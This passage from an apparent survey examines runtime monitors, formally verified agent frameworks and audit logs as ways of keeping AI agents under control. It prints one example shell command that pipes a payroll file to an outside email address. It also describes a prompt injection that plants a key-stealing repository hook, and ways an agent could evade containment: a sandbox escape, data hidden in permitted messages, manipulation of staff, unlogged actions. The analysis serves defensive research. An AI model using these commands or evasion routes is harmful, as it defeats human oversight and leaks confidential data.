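Replacing "three steps" with "three minutes" also causes trouble. The rule remains a safety property, but, as Schneider points out, stopping a program does not stop time. Basin, Jugé and colleagues (2012), in *Enforceable Security Policies Revisited*, built a theory on this point by dividing actions into those that a monitor can prevent and those that it can only observe, such as the tick of a clock. One of their examples is almost the office rule: a delivery must follow every request within three time units, unless the system stops first. Their proof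 that no monitor can enforce it is short:

1. A request followed by three ticks complies, because the delivery may still come before the fourth tick. The monitor must therefore accept this trace.
2. The monitor cannot prevent a tick, so it must also accept whatever trace the next tick produces.
3. The next tick produces a request followed by four ticks without a delivery, which breaks the rule.

Basin and colleagues contrast this with a rule that forbids logging in for three time units after a failure. The monitor cannot prevent the failure or the clock ticks, but it can refuse the login, and only a login can break the rule. In general, a monitor can enforce a rule only if it can prevent every step that would complete a violation. They also show that if a finite automaton can express a rule, an algorithm can determine whether the rule is enforceable. No such algorithm exists for the context-free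 languages, a larger class that can describe nested structures of any depth.

The office can instead require that no payment leaves before its review. The monitor can enforce this rule because only a payment can break it, and the monitor can hold payments back. The rule does not guarantee that a review ever takes place. A duty to review within three minutes remains unenforceable, since the monitor cannot make a person look at an invoice. But the monitor can track the time and send a flag itself, so "reviewed or flagged within three minutes" is achievable as long as the monitor keeps running and its flag arrives in time.

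### Holding the request

Real monitors can do more than stop a program. Ligatti, Bauer and Walker (2005), in *Enforcing Non-safety Security Policies with Program Monitors*, studied edit automata, which can suppress an action and insert actions on the program's behalf. They required enforcement to be sound, meaning that whatever reaches the outside world complies with the rule. They also required it to be transparent, meaning that the monitor preserves the effect of runs that already comply, which excludes a monitor that stops everything.

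An edit automaton can enforce even the "eventually" version of the office rule. When the agent requests a payment, the automaton withholds the request and every action after it. When the review comes, the automaton releases the whole sequence in its original order, so every released request has a review. If no review comes, nothing in the sequence takes effect. The automaton therefore doesn't need to determine whether a review will come, which is impossible from a finite trace.

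Ligatti and colleagues prove that edit automata can do this for every reasonable "infinite renewal property". A rule is in this class if an infinite run complies exactly when it complies at infinitely many points along the way. The class includes every safety property, some liveness properties and some rules that are neither. The office rule qualifies because each review returns the run to a point where no request is waiting.

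In this model the program's actions form a fixed sequence, so withholding one does not change what the program does next. A real agent may need the answer to a request before it can continue. *Kairos* has to handle such agents. It holds their effects at the edge of a virtual machine, where a monitor can release, refuse or defer each one. The monitor follows a written policy. It releases an effect if the values that determine it, such as the recipient of a payment, come from a source the operator trusts and the data is allowed to go to its destination. It refuses what an explicit rule forbids and defers the rest.

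If the agent needs only a confirmation, a proxy holds its network request while the agent continues with a stand-in reply. The monitor also holds later effects that may depend on this reply. Before anything becomes irreversible, a language model or a person reviews the held effects, along with what the agent did next, and either commits or discards them. If the agent needs the actual content of a web page, a stand-in reply won't work, and the decision must be made before the request is sent.

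Waiting can expose an attack that is not apparent from a single action. In one example, a web guide leads an agent to install a script that runs whenever the agent saves its work to the code repository. The write looks like ordinary set-up, so the monitor defers it. At the next save, the script tries to send a private key to an attacker. The policy blocks this, and there is then enough evidence to discard the script too.

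*Kairos* guarantees that every effect passes through the monitor, that no effect becomes irreversible before the monitor releases it, and that a refused effect is never visible outside. These guarantees hold whatever the agent does and whatever the monitor decides, but they depend on effect exclusivity, a correct host and monitor, and a model provider that does not collude with the attacker. They do not cover whether the monitor releases the right effects, which has to be measured.

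On AgentDojo, a benchmark that plants hostile instructions in what an agent reads, attacks succeeded in 47.0 per cent of 629 cases without a defence and in 2.7 per cent with Kairos. Without an attack, the protected agent completed 85.1 per cent of its tasks. A strict version, which refused everything the policy could not clear, completed 42.7 per cent, and attacks succeeded about as often. The difference in completed tasks probably overstates the value of holding actions, because the strict version also lacked the language model that decides the deferred cases. The experiments used simulated tools connected through an adapter, so they did not test the virtual machine's boundary.

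Holding an action makes a task less likely to succeed when later steps depend on that action. On AgentDyn, a benchmark of open-ended tasks, the agent under attack completed 37.1 per cent of its tasks with Kairos and 55.5 per cent without it. Tasks that had to continue past one held effect succeeded at 90 per cent of their usual rate, and those with two or more at 62 per cent. After a refusal, the stand-in reply also remains in the model's context, so the monitor has to tell the agent that the action never took effect. An office agent waiting for several reviews would likewise be planning around payments that may never go out.

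### One solver query per rule

*VIGIL* (Li, Chen and colleagues, 2026) turns each decision into a question for a solver, a program that determines whether a set of logical statements can all be true together. The monitor first converts the agent's tool calls into events, each with an action, named arguments, a status and an excerpt of the output. A language model translates the written rules into a small formal language. The solver then checks the events against one rule at a time. If they contradict the rule, the run has broken it, and the smallest set of conditions that causes the contradiction identifies the event responsible.

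The language has a form for "a review follows later", one for "a review follows within the next *n* events" and one for "a payment only after a review". It also has variables, which solve the problem of the wrong invoice. Suppose the trace contains a review of invoice 18 and the agent now wants to pay invoice 17. The requirement for this payment is:

If the event is a payment of invoice *x*, some earlier event is a review of invoice *x*.

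The facts set *x* to 17, but the only earlier review concerns invoice 18. The solver finds a contradiction, so the monitor blocks the payment.

The form of the rule matters here as much as in the theory. Li and colleagues check prohibitions and preconditions before the pending call goes ahead, but they check an obligation that waits for a later event when the run ends. If the office writes its rule as "a review follows", it learns of a missed review after the payment, whereas the monitor can block an unreviewed payment if the rule is "a payment only after a review".

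In a test on 152 recorded agent runs, 72 of which broke a rule, the system detected 69 of the 72 and raised 8 false alarms on the other 80. AgentSpec, a monitor that evaluates its rules at each proposed action, detected 34. A language model that read the whole trace detected 48 and raised 5 false alarms. The system took an average of 4.38 seconds per run, including 4.05 seconds to translate the rules and 0.27 seconds for the solver's check.

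The errors arise in recording events and in translating rules. In the two examples here, the solver itself reasoned correctly. In one missed violation, the agent ran a script that was supposed to make an encrypted archive. The script wrote the archive unencrypted, then deleted the original without the integrity check that the rule required first. Both steps happened inside the script and produced no events. The solver treats the trace as complete, so anything missing from it counts as not having happened. In one false alarm, the language model dropped the word "bulk" when translating a rule about bulk calendar changes, so the monitor flagged the moving of a single appointment.

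Li and colleagues also ran the monitor on 216 executions of published skills, which are packages of instructions and tools for agents. It raised 44 alerts, and they confirmed 34 of them. In one case, a workflow from NVIDIA set no limit on retries, and the agent kept resubmitting failed, expensive jobs. For safety, the researchers had replaced the external programs with stubs that only logged the calls, so the study shows what the monitor would have blocked.

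### Rules about amounts

The solver's queries always have an answer because they concern only a finite number of recorded events and values, not how the run might continue. A monitor that considers every possible continuation can reach a verdict earlier, but some rules about data have no such monitor.

Gianola and colleagues explain this with an agent that looks for a concert ticket. Under the rule, the agent must always keep the cheapest offer so far and must finally settle on ticket 123, which costs 100 euros. Once it has bookmarked a ticket for 95 euros, it can't return to ticket 123 without breaking the first requirement. A monitor that considers how the run could continue reports a permanent violation immediately, while one that evaluates only the trace so far may have to wait until the end of the run.

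For rules built from a fixed list of events, such as the office rule in its first form, an algorithm can always compute these verdicts. But if rules can also add amounts and compare them from one event to the next, no monitoring procedure can give the right verdict for every rule. Such rules can describe the steps of a counting machine as powerful as any computer, and no algorithm can predict in every case whether such a machine will reach a given state.

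The remedy is to restrict the rules. Gianola and colleagues prove that monitoring is possible for rules that look values up in a fixed database and compare them without adding them, provided that no chain of look-ups leads back to its starting type. The ticket rule meets these conditions, and "a payment needs a reviewer whose approval limit is at least the payment amount" does too, with suitable tables. Monitoring is also possible if there is a fixed limit on how many steps back the comparisons reach.

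The rule "The payments since the last review must stay below 10,000 euros" falls outside both groups because it needs a running total over any number of payments. The office's monitor could still add up the payments and report when they reach the limit. For more complicated rules with totals, though, it might be unable to recognise a violation as soon as it becomes unavoidable, so the company's flag might come too late to change anything.

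### Several monitors on one workflow

A payment may have to satisfy one rule about the order of events and another about the text sent with it, and one monitor rarely suits both. *One Monitor Does Not Fit All* (Ferrando, October 2026) tested two monitors on a workflow for computer incidents. One checked the order of events. A repair needed an approval within the last six steps and a backup within the last three, and a report to outsiders had to carry a label marking it as free of secrets. The other checked the report's text and destination but had no information about approvals. An operation went ahead only if neither monitor rejected it.

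Ferrando ran seven scripted sequences with 34 requests, of which six were unsafe.

| Active monitors | Unsafe requests carried out, of 6 | Safe requests blocked, of 28 |
|---|---|---|
| None | 6 | 0 |
| Order only | 2 | 0 |
| Report only | 2 | 0 |
| Both | 0 | 0 |

The order monitor let through a report to an unapproved address and a secret report with a false label. The report monitor let through a repair without approval and one whose approval had expired. No language model chose the actions, and Ferrando designed the cases to need both monitors, so the table doesn't measure error rates for real agents. It does show that the two monitors can control the same operations without interfering with each other.

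In a second experiment, one part of the software gave the approval and another sent the report. Each report needed an approval for its own incident. Both monitors stayed active, and Ferrando varied only what the order monitor observed.

| What the order monitor observed | Unsafe reports sent, of 6 | Safe reports blocked, of 2 |
|---|---|---|
| Both parts, with incident numbers | 0 | 0 |
| Both parts, without incident numbers | 1 | 0 |
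| Only the part that sends reports | 0 | 2 |

Without the incident numbers, an approval for incident A also covered a report on incident B, so a violation was missed. Without the approvals, no report could pass, which caused false alarms.

Ferrando states the condition that the monitor's view must meet. If obs(τ) is what the monitor receives from a trace τ, and *b*(τ) is the correct answer for that trace, then for any two possible traces:

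obs(τ) = obs(τ′) implies *b*(τ) = *b*(τ′)

If two traces look the same to a monitor but need different verdicts, the monitor cannot judge both correctly. It can reject both to be safe, but then it also blocks legitimate work.

Filtering also changes what counts as a step. If somebody stops sending file reads to the office's five-state automaton to save time, then in the run above it receives neither event 7 nor event 8, so it stays in "two left" and reports no violation. The automaton still works as designed, but "within three steps" no longer counts file reads.

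If the monitor blocks every request while it is in the "violated" state, one late review on Monday will stop all payments for the rest of the week. Ferrando separates the record of past violations from the decision on the current request, so a valid request can succeed after an earlier one has failed. Resetting the monitor instead would be risky, because it may also erase the record of a withdrawn approval.

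Ferrando proves that a set of monitors keeps unsafe effects out if four conditions hold:

- Every effect passes a point where the monitors can hold it.
- The system handles decisions and effects one at a time, so each decision takes account of everything already done.
- At least one mandatory monitor rejects every effect that would break the rules.
- A rejection, or the failure of a monitor to answer, actually stops the effect.

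The proof is by induction. No effects have occurred at the start, and each released effect keeps the record within the rules. The last condition depends partly on how the operator configures the system. Letting requests pass when a monitor times out keeps the business running, but those requests are neither checked nor flagged unless the timeout itself raises a flag.

An agent that makes several calls at once can easily break the second condition. Suppose one review entitles the agent to pay invoice 17 once, and the agent sends two payment calls simultaneously. Each check finds the review and no earlier payment, so both payments go out. To prevent this, the system has to check and release each payment as one indivisible step before it begins to check the next. Listing the payments in order in a log afterwards does not prevent the second payment.

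## A verified agent framework that treats the model as unpredictable

Ferrando's conditions describe what a set of monitors must do, but someone must still show that the running program does it. For an AI agent, much of that program is the agent framework, the ordinary software that calls the language model, reads its reply and carries out the actions specified in it. In *Containment Verification*, Moon and Varshney (2026) proved that a small framework follows a policy whatever the model replies.

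They used Dafny, a programming language whose verifier checks code against conditions written into the code. In their program, the model is a procedure with a return type but no body, so the verifier has to allow for every value of that type. This technique is known as havoc, and the dafny-lang community's *Dafny Reference Manual* describes the result as "some arbitrary (but type-consistent) value". The proof covers a model that picks its replies at random and one that behaves well for a thousand steps and then turns hostile.

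Moon and Varshney call the returned value an action, but at that point nothing has happened yet, so "request" is the clearer word.

### A toy agent with three requests

Suppose the office agent can return only three kinds of request: Read(*path*), Send(*address*) and Finish. It may read files only in the shared folder, write only to staff, and take at most 20 steps. In simplified form, the framework looks like this:

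```
method GetRequest() returns (a: Request)   // no body: a can be anything

repeat until stopped:
  a := GetRequest()
  if a is Read(p) and p is in the shared folder:  read p
  else if a is Send(r) and r is on the staff list:  send to r
  else if a is Finish:  stop
  else:  do nothing
  steps := steps + 1
  if steps == 20:  stop
```

Moon and Varshney describe such a program as a labelled transition system, which has sets of states, requests and boundary events, a starting state and a list of possible steps. A boundary event is what the framework does at its border with the outside world, which here is reading a file, sending a message or doing nothing. The state holds the number of steps so far, the files read and the addresses written to. Each step has the form (*s*, *a*, *e*, *s*′), which means that in state *s*, the request *a* leads to the event *e* and the new state *s*′.

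| Request | Boundary event | Steps so far |
|---|---|---|
| Read a price list in the shared folder | file read | 1 |
| Send to a rival company | nothing | 2 |
| Send to Anna, who is on the staff list | message sent | 3 |

Every state must have at least one step for every request, so the framework can't get stuck on an unexpected request. It refuses a request by taking a step whose event is "nothing".

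The boundary policy is a condition Π(*s*, *a*, *e*, *s*′) on a single step. In the toy example, it allows file reads only from the shared folder and messages only to people on the staff list, and it requires the step count in *s*′ to be at most 20. The model may request anything, since the policy restricts only what the framework does in response. A policy of this kind cannot require that the agent's messages be true, because truth depends on what the text means.

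For the toy, one could prove that the policy holds by checking each branch. A real framework also tracks the conversation, its place in the workflow and much else, so Moon and Varshney use two transition systems. The abstract model *M* contains only what the policy needs, and the detailed model *I* describes the framework as it operates. In the toy, *M* has the counter and the two lists, while *I* also has the text of every message. A state of *M* matches a state of *I* if their counters and lists agree, and the action "message to Anna" in *M* matches "message to Anna with this text" in *I*.

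They first prove that *M* obeys its policy Π<sub>M</sub> for every possible sequence of requests. Then they prove three conditions that connect the models:

- **R1:** The two starting states match.
- **R2:** If two states match and *I* takes a step on some request, *M* can take a step on the same request, with a matching event, and the new states match too.
- **R3:** If the step of *M* in such a pair obeys Π<sub>M</sub>, the step of *I* obeys its own policy Π<sub>I</sub>.

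The soundness theorem says that *I* then obeys Π<sub>I</sub> at every step, whatever the model returns. Its proof is an induction over an arbitrary sequence of requests:

1. The starting states match, by R1.
2. If the states match before a request, R2 gives *M* a step on that request after which they match again. *M* therefore has a complete run that follows *I* request by request.
3. Every step of that run obeys Π<sub>M</sub>, because *M* obeys it for all sequences of requests.
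4. By R3, every step of *I* obeys Π<sub>I</sub>.

Suppose a programmer adds a branch that resends messages after a network error, and forgets to check the staff list. In some state, *I* can then send a message to the rival company, but *M* has no matching step, so R2 fails and Dafny reports the error. This is the same kind of mistake as a missing hook in Linux, except that here the verifier covers every branch of the model.

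The theorem does not require the framework to be useful or to flag the actions it refuses. A framework that answered every request with "nothing" would satisfy it. If the agent tries to write to the rival company twenty times, the framework refuses each attempt but need not report any of them.

### PocketFlow

Moon and Varshney applied the method to PocketFlow, an open-source framework of about 100 lines. As Pocket Flow's own page explains, a workflow in it is a graph whose nodes each handle a task and whose labelled edges determine which node comes next. The proof concerns the loop that moves from node to node. This loop accepts four kinds of request, and three invariants hold at every point of every run:

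- Every path in the record of file reads starts with the path of the workspace folder.
- Every tool in the record of tool calls is on the list of allowed tools.
- The number of steps stays within a fixed limit.

These properties are modest. The tool invariant covers only which tool the agent calls, so if the mail tool is on the list, a message to anyone satisfies it. The file invariant covers only how a path begins. The path `/shared/../payroll` begins with `/shared`, but the two dots lead out of that folder, so other code has to resolve such paths before the test. The proof also doesn't cover running nodes in parallel, which PocketFlow allows.

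Language models wrote the specification and the proofs. Claude Sonnet 4.6 explored the source code, and Claude Opus 4.7 wrote the Dafny files and repaired the proofs that failed. This hardly matters for the proofs, because the verifier checks them regardless of who wrote them. It matters more for the specification, because the verifier cannot check whether a property is the one people wanted.

The evaluation covered four runs across two workflows, an agent that reads files and one that retrieves documents to answer questions. Dafny accepted all the final proofs, taking 1.2 to 2.5 seconds for each path through a workflow. Each run used 1.6 to 3.4 million tokens. That is very little work compared with the 20 person-years seL4 took, although seL4 is almost ninety times as long. Dafny then translated the verified code into Python, where the procedure without a body becomes a call that fetches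 the model's real reply. In tests that mixed permitted and forbidden requests, the Python program recorded only permitted events.

*Methods for Formal Verification of Agent Skills* (2026) also treats the model as an adversary that may do anything. It says testing should be enough for most skills, and reserves proof for the few that can do serious damage, for example by making payments.

### Effects outside the interface

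Moon and Varshney name three ways a deployed system could still fail. The framework may contain a step that the abstract model does not allow, an effect may bypass the interface, or the policy may not express what people intended. Dafny catches only the first, by rejecting the proof.

The theorem applies to real files and messages only if every effect goes through the verified interface, an assumption called effect exclusivity. Direct Python calls, open network access, a bug in the Python runtime, a kernel flaw or a hardware fault can each break this assumption, even though the proof remains valid.

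This can easily happen with PocketFlow. It has no built-in tools, so the office would write its own mail tool in Python, and that code could open files and network connections directly. Suppose the tool downloads the company logo from the web for each message. The framework records one permitted tool call but no event for the download. If the agent can influence the logo's address, it can use the download to send data out.

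There is also unverified code between the model and the verified loop. A parser must turn the model's text into one of the four kinds of request, and the proof assumes that the parser does nothing else. A parser that executed part of the text while reading it would let the model act before the verified loop received any request.

Moon and Varshney therefore recommend running the framework inside a sandbox, which restricts what the whole process can reach. They class sandboxes as having only empirical support, and mention Copy Fail, a Linux kernel flaw that gives an ordinary program administrator rights and went unnoticed for nearly a decade, until April 2026. They are right about sandboxes built on Linux, but the seL4 kernel has a proof that its barriers hold for every program, so a sandbox built on it can have the same kind of guarantee as the framework.

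### Rules that are true because nothing happens

The statement "Every payment above a million euros has two signatures" is true of an office that never makes such a payment. Logicians call such a statement vacuously true. According to *Bounded Loops* (2026), Beer and colleagues described this problem in automatic verification in 2001 and gave an efficient way to detect it, and commercial verification tools now routinely check for it.

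Moon and Varshney knew of the danger and put three gates in front of the final proof:

- The Dafny files must parse and pass the type checker within 30 seconds.
- If one removes most of the proof's content, verification must fail.
- If a language model plants a plausible error in the proof, verification must fail.

They also worried that a language model with access to the code would write a specification that merely described it. So in the normal mode, the model derived the safety property without access to the implementation. For comparison, they repeated the work with access to it.

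The document-retrieval workflow exposed a weakness. In that workflow, the effect to control is the reading of documents, and each document must be on a list of allowed ones. The template for the safety property had no field for documents. It had only the fields for file reads, tool calls and steps. The two modes dealt with this differently:

```
without access to the code:
  when a document is read, add it to tool_calls,
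  and it must be on the list of allowed tools

with access to the code:
  tool_calls never changes
```

Without access, the model treated documents as tools. The resulting rule has misleading names, but it does restrict which documents the agent reads. With access, the model noted that this workflow had no list of tools and left the field empty. The rule "Every tool call is on the list" was then true in every run because there were no tool calls, and no rule covered the documents. Both versions passed all three gates, and Dafny verified both.

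The gates missed the problem because they damaged the central part of the proof, which was sound, and tested whether Dafny detected the damage. None of them tested whether the list of tool calls could ever contain an entry. Moon and Varshney propose such a test for every field but had not built it. In terms of completeness, the scope *S* had shrunk to exclude the documents, and the verifier's output did not show this.

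The empty rule arose only in the comparison mode and in one workflow, so these runs don't show how common the problem is. Studies of ordinary programs suggest that specifications often require very little. In *Verified but Vacuous*, Vempaty, Sompalle and colleagues (2026) rebuilt a published system in which a language model writes Dafny programs. On one set of tasks, Dafny accepted 99.1 per cent of the programs. Of the accepted programs, 94.7 per cent stated no condition on their result, and only 1.9 per cent used a property defined in the separate specification. The researchers caution that a program that uses no such property can still state a meaningful condition of its own. The system's prompt also asked for test values instead of general conditions.

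*DafnyCert* (Silva, Amaral and colleagues, 2026) searches for wrong programs that satisfy the same specification as the right one. One method calculates how many rungs a ladder needs, but its specification requires only a non-negative answer, so a program that always returns 0 also verifies. For a ladder with a single rung at height 463 and a largest allowed gap of 1, the original method returns 462. A benchmark had labelled this specification "strong", meaning that it allows only one result for each input. Among the benchmark's files with a single method, 70.2 per cent of the specifications labelled "strong" were weak.

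Experts make such mistakes too. Silva and colleagues cite IronFleet, a verified distributed system whose style of proof Moon and Varshney adopted. Other researchers disabled the part of IronFleet that discards duplicate requests, and the system still passed verification because its specification did not require each request to take effect only once.

An agent's policy should allow many behaviours, so it would be wrong to require a single result. But it would still help to search for wrong programs that pass verification. PocketFlow's gates altered only the proof. If someone had also removed the list of allowed documents from the workflow, the empty specification would probably still have verified, exposing the gap.

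### Why a shell command empties the guarantee

Suppose the office adds a fourth request to the toy agent, Run(*command*), which passes a line of text to the computer's command shell. The agent now returns this:

```
Run("cat /payroll/salaries | mail rival@example.com")
```

The framework produces one event, "command run", which the new policy permits. It records no file reads or messages, so the lists checked by the rules about files and recipients are empty and, as with the documents, the rules hold for that reason. The proof still covers every value the model can return, but one value can now be any program, so the proof establishes only that the framework ran what the agent asked it to run. Moon and Varshney warn that a general shell or a command that evaluates code reduces the guarantee to whatever holds for that command.

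The office could try to inspect the text. A list of permitted commands is not enough, because a command that looks harmless can start another program. For example, `find` searches for files but can also run a program on each file it finds. No procedure can determine what every program will do. *CARE* (2026), a guard for agents that use a shell, first converts a command into a standard form, then applies fixed rules about risk and uses a language model to judge borderline cases. With such a guard, the office would rely on a measured error rate instead of the proof.

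Companies still have a strong reason to accept the shell. In *Is Bash All You Need?*, Mak, Suresh and colleagues (2026) gave two models the same office tasks through different interfaces. The tasks came from TheAgentCompany, which simulates work in a software company, and APEX-Agents, which covers banking, consulting and law. The scores below are percentages, with Opus 4.8 first and GPT-5.5 second.

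| Interface | TheAgentCompany | APEX-Agents |
|---|---|---|
| Fixed tools, called one at a time | 44.9 / 45.3 | 41.1 / 39.8 |
| Programs that may call only the fixed tools | 52.9 / 45.1 | 40.1 / 37.8 |
| Shell alone | 69.4 / 67.1 | 48.5 / 44.6 |

The shell also used fewer tokens than separate tool calls. The large difference on TheAgentCompany may depend partly on the set of 60 tools, which the researchers had to build because the benchmark has none. They recommend the shell where an organisation can isolate what the agent runs, and programs that call fixed tools where policy requires an approved list. Those programs would suit containment verification because each of their effects still goes through a typed call, though somebody would have to trust or verify the restricted environment that runs them.

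### Agenra

PocketFlow's invariants do not cover where a message's text came from or whether anyone approved it. *Agenra* (Ammanaghatta Shivakumar, Priya and Gao, 2026) describes a monitor that tracks both. Its core is written in Lean, a programming language and proof checker, and some of the proofs are about the same functions that run when the agent makes a call.

In the main example, an agent must send Alice the public parts of a private report, once. The policy requires the text to come from a tool called Sanitize, which selects the public fields, and the address to come from a particular directory lookup. The monitor counts an attempt before the mail tool runs. The attempt still counts if the tool fails, so the agent cannot send a second message by claiming that the first one failed.

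The Lean proofs establish, among other things, that no permission exceeds its quota and that a text accepted as coming from Sanitize really has that recorded origin. They assume that calls happen one at a time. They also leave a good deal to trust:

- Python code translates the policy, passes calls to Lean and must then run exactly the call that Lean checked.
- Each tool must do only what its declaration states.
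- Sanitize must really remove the private fields.
- The directory must return Alice's real address.

Agenra also depends on effect exclusivity. It separates the agent from the monitor within one Python process, but this separation does not hold if the agent can run its own Python code.

A company can also require a person's approval for a call. The approval is a permit for one operation with exact arguments. If the agent edits the summary after the reviewer approves it, the permit no longer matches. Nor does the permit match a newly produced summary, even an identical one. The paper proves that every protected call that reaches its tool has used up a matching permit issued earlier in the same task, and that no permit can be used twice. This also prevents two simultaneous payments from relying on one review, provided that the system actually handles calls one at a time.

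The theorem cannot show that the reviewer judged well. A reviewer who approves the summary after studying it for ten minutes and one who approves it unread both cause the same event, the issue of a permit. Under Ferrando's condition, a monitor cannot give different verdicts on traces that look the same to it, so it cannot distinguish these two reviewers. Proving more would require a formal definition of a good decision, and a monitor with that definition could make the decision itself. In one analysis, Ammanaghatta Shivakumar and colleagues let the simulated reviewer approve every message, so that the other rules had to stop the bad ones.

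The researchers' first policy required the text to be public but did not require it to come from Sanitize, so the agent could send Alice unrelated public text. The monitor enforced this policy correctly, but when the researchers replayed calls recorded from live agents, the policy allowed five that it should have refused. A new rule on the text's origin stopped all five. The revised policy still accepts text that an attacker wrote and the agent passed through Sanitize, and blocking that text requires another rule.

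To detect policies too strict to be useful, Agenra also searches a model of the task for a run that completes it. If there is neither a forbidden run nor a useful one, it reports the result as vacuous. For the report task, the shortest useful run has six events. With a limit of eight events, the search visited 12.3 million points and took 154 seconds, so it suits only short workflows.

Widening a permission can block a workflow that used to work. Suppose one permission allows the agent to delete file B once, and the next allows it to delete file A once. Somebody widens the first to "A or B". The monitor always counts an action against the first permission that fits, so deleting A now uses up that permission. The agent can then delete A a second time, but it can no longer delete B. Agenra can certify that a change keeps all the old workflows possible. In a test with 51 changes, it certified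 all 21 that kept them possible and none of the 30 that didn't. A certified change can still allow new actions. For example, Agenra certifies raising the limit on messages to Alice from one to two, because every old workflow still works, though the agent can now send a second message if a reviewer approves it.

In trials with live agents, fixed attacks made an unguarded Qwen model send the private report in 15 of 20 cases and an unguarded Hermes model in 1 of 20. With Agenra, neither model sent it. A guard the researchers wrote by hand did equally well, so these trials show no advantage from the proofs. Under attack, Qwen completed only 5 of the 20 tasks and Hermes only 10, with or without a guard.

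### Does the guarantee hold for more capable models?

Moon and Varshney argue that their guarantee does not weaken as models become more capable, because their proof depends on a piece of ordinary software matching its specification. Training a model to behave well, or reading its reasoning for signs of trouble, by contrast, depends on facts about the model that may change with the next version.

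This is correct for the theorem itself, which covers every sequence of requests, so a more capable model cannot produce one that it leaves out. The conference abstract of *Containment Verification* states the claim with the necessary restriction, "over the modeled typed action boundary".

Effect exclusivity is less stable. Installing a new model does not change the software or its undiscovered bugs, but a more capable agent is more likely to find them. An agent that found a flaw like Copy Fail could leave the sandbox if it could first run its own code, for instance through a bug in the parser or in a tool. The assumption would then be false even though the framework had not changed.

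A more capable agent can also do more with the requests it is allowed to make. If it is allowed to write to staff, it could persuade one of them to forward a contract using only messages that comply with the policy. Moon and Varshney exclude manipulation and deception from their claim for this reason. They do list the theft of confidential data among the dangers that a narrow interface prevents. Such an interface blocks messages to unapproved addresses, but an agent can still hide data in a message to an approved one.

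The interface may not stay narrow either. Agents score higher with a shell, but a company that gives them one loses most of what the proof guarantees.

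## Whether a log can show that nothing was left out of it

A company that gives its agent a shell can prove little about a command before it runs, so it has to rely more on the log afterwards. Cryptography can show that nobody has changed the log since the agent's software wrote it, but not that the software wrote an entry for every action. Without evidence that every action was logged, the company cannot use the log to support a claim such as "the agent sent no other emails".

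### What a hash chain protects

A hash function turns a text of any length into a short fingerprint, and changing one letter of the text gives a completely different fingerprint. In a hash chain, each log entry contains the hash of the entry before it. The office agent's log might look like this:

```
1  read the price list          previous: none
2  sent email to Anna           previous: hash of entry 1
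3  sent email to the law firm   previous: hash of entry 2
```

Suppose somebody later replaces Anna's name in entry 2. The hash of entry 2 then no longer matches the copy in entry 3. To hide the change, they would have to recompute entry 3 and every entry after it. Anyone who controls the whole file can do this in seconds, so the chain also needs a safeguard outside the file, such as a copy of the latest hash kept by another party, or signatures on the entries from a separate service with its own key. The last entry needs this most, because no later entry contains its hash. *Bounded Loops* points out that this entry holds the final verdict on a run, so somebody who wanted to make a failed run look successful would change it.

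Bindschaedler, Botha and Siebenbrunner (2026), in *Agent Flight Recorder*, describe a recorder for agents that stores its hashes outside. It collects events in batches, combines their hashes in pairs, then combines the results in pairs, and continues until one hash remains. If *M*<sub>*t*</sub> is this combined hash for batch *t*, the recorder publishes the following value on a public blockchain:

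*R*<sub>*t*</sub> = *H*(*M*<sub>*t*</sub>, *R*<sub>*t*−1</sub>)

With batches of 100 events, an auditor needs about seven other hashes to confirm that an event belongs to its batch. If somebody removes a whole batch, the next batch still refers to it. Publishing the hashes cost $2.30 per 100,000 events. In tests on artificial workloads, the system detected every edited, deleted or reordered entry and every attempt to show different histories to different people, and it raised no false alarms.

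Suppose the office agent sends a fourth email and the software never writes an entry for it. The next entry will contain the hash of entry 3, so the chain will be intact and every signature valid. Bindschaedler and colleagues therefore explicitly exclude completeness from their goals. Their system protects the integrity of the events that reach the recorder, but it does not guarantee that every event reaches it. If an attacker takes over the computer, the older entries remain protected, but new ones may be false.

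An entry can also be genuine but cover less than it seems to. Ghanem and Al-Bander (2026), in *Who Audits Whom, on What Substrate, with What Evidence?*, report measurements from a register of 3,413 public web addresses. Its operator had to exclude 82 of them because the program that read the addresses might have read only part of the response. In 74 of these cases, it had stopped at exactly 8,388,608 bytes, its limit. A signed hash of such a reading would be correct, but only for the first part of the page. Ghanem and Al-Bander want every important record to state whether the observation finished, what it was drawn from and what it excluded. This would help honest operators, but readers would still have to trust whoever wrote the statement.

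### Fields that nobody recorded

*Auditable Agents* (Nian, Yuan and colleagues, 2026) lists five things an auditor must be able to establish: what the agent did, in what circumstances, whether it complied with the policy, who was responsible, and whether the evidence is intact. It grades the last on a scale from no protection, through append-only and hash-chained logs, to signed logs. Even a signed log can still be useless for establishing the other four.

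They also distinguish between logging an action and recording enough detail to reconstruct it. If the office log contains "queried the customer database" without the query, an auditor cannot tell what the agent looked up. Missing fields can make a rule undecidable, meaning that the records establish neither compliance nor violation. Nian and colleagues prove that if a rule depends on a certain field, and no relevant entry contains it, the rule is undecidable however many entries there are. An auditor with 20,000 entries that read "email sent", without an address, cannot tell whether any email went to a rival.

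A missing entry can also change what the remaining ones mean. In one example from Nian and colleagues, a policy check blocks an agent's email, the agent changes the text, and a person approves the second attempt. If the log contains only the email that went out, an auditor cannot tell whether the agent was doing ordinary work or getting around the policy. Recording blocked attempts need not slow the agent down much. A gate from the same research group, which logs allowed, blocked and pending tool calls separately, added a median of 8.3 milliseconds per call. Nian and colleagues leave open how to tell from a record whether a step never happened or was just not recorded.

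Without a log, an auditor can recover only a little information. One method hides statistical signals in the text each agent writes, so that an auditor can later work out which agent wrote a passage. It attributed 82 to 87 per cent of the text correctly, but it cannot establish whether the agents followed a rule.

### Three emails, two entries

Zhao (2026), in *Auditable Claims about AI Agents*, proves that an auditor cannot fill this gap by reasoning more cleverly about the same log. The proof concerns claims about many actions, such as "a person approves every external email". Before anyone reads the records, such a claim must name its policy, the actions and period it covers, the records that would settle it, who writes them, and the rule for reaching a verdict. "Our agent is safe" names none of these. For a properly stated claim, there are three verdicts:

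- Supported: the evidence shows that the records include every action in scope, and each action complies with the policy.
- Contradicted: the records establish that some action in scope violated the policy.
- Undecidable: the records establish neither, and the auditor names the record that is missing.

Suppose the agent sends emails *a* and *b* with a person's approval and email *c* without it. Its software logs *a* and *b* but leaves out *c*. An auditor who has only this log can't exclude either of two histories, which Zhao calls worlds:

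| | Emails sent | Entries in the log | "A person approved every email" |
|---|---|---|---|
| World 1 | a, b | a, b | true |
| World 2 | a, b, c | a, b | false |

A decision rule is sound if it returns "supported" only when the claim is true and "contradicted" only when it is false. Zhao's lemma is that a sound rule must return "undecidable" when two worlds produce the same records and the claim is true in only one of them. The proof is short:

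1. The rule uses only the records, so it returns the same verdict in both worlds.
2. "Supported" would be wrong in World 2, and "contradicted" would be wrong in World 1.
3. This leaves "undecidable".

Ferrando's condition for monitors rests on the same reasoning.

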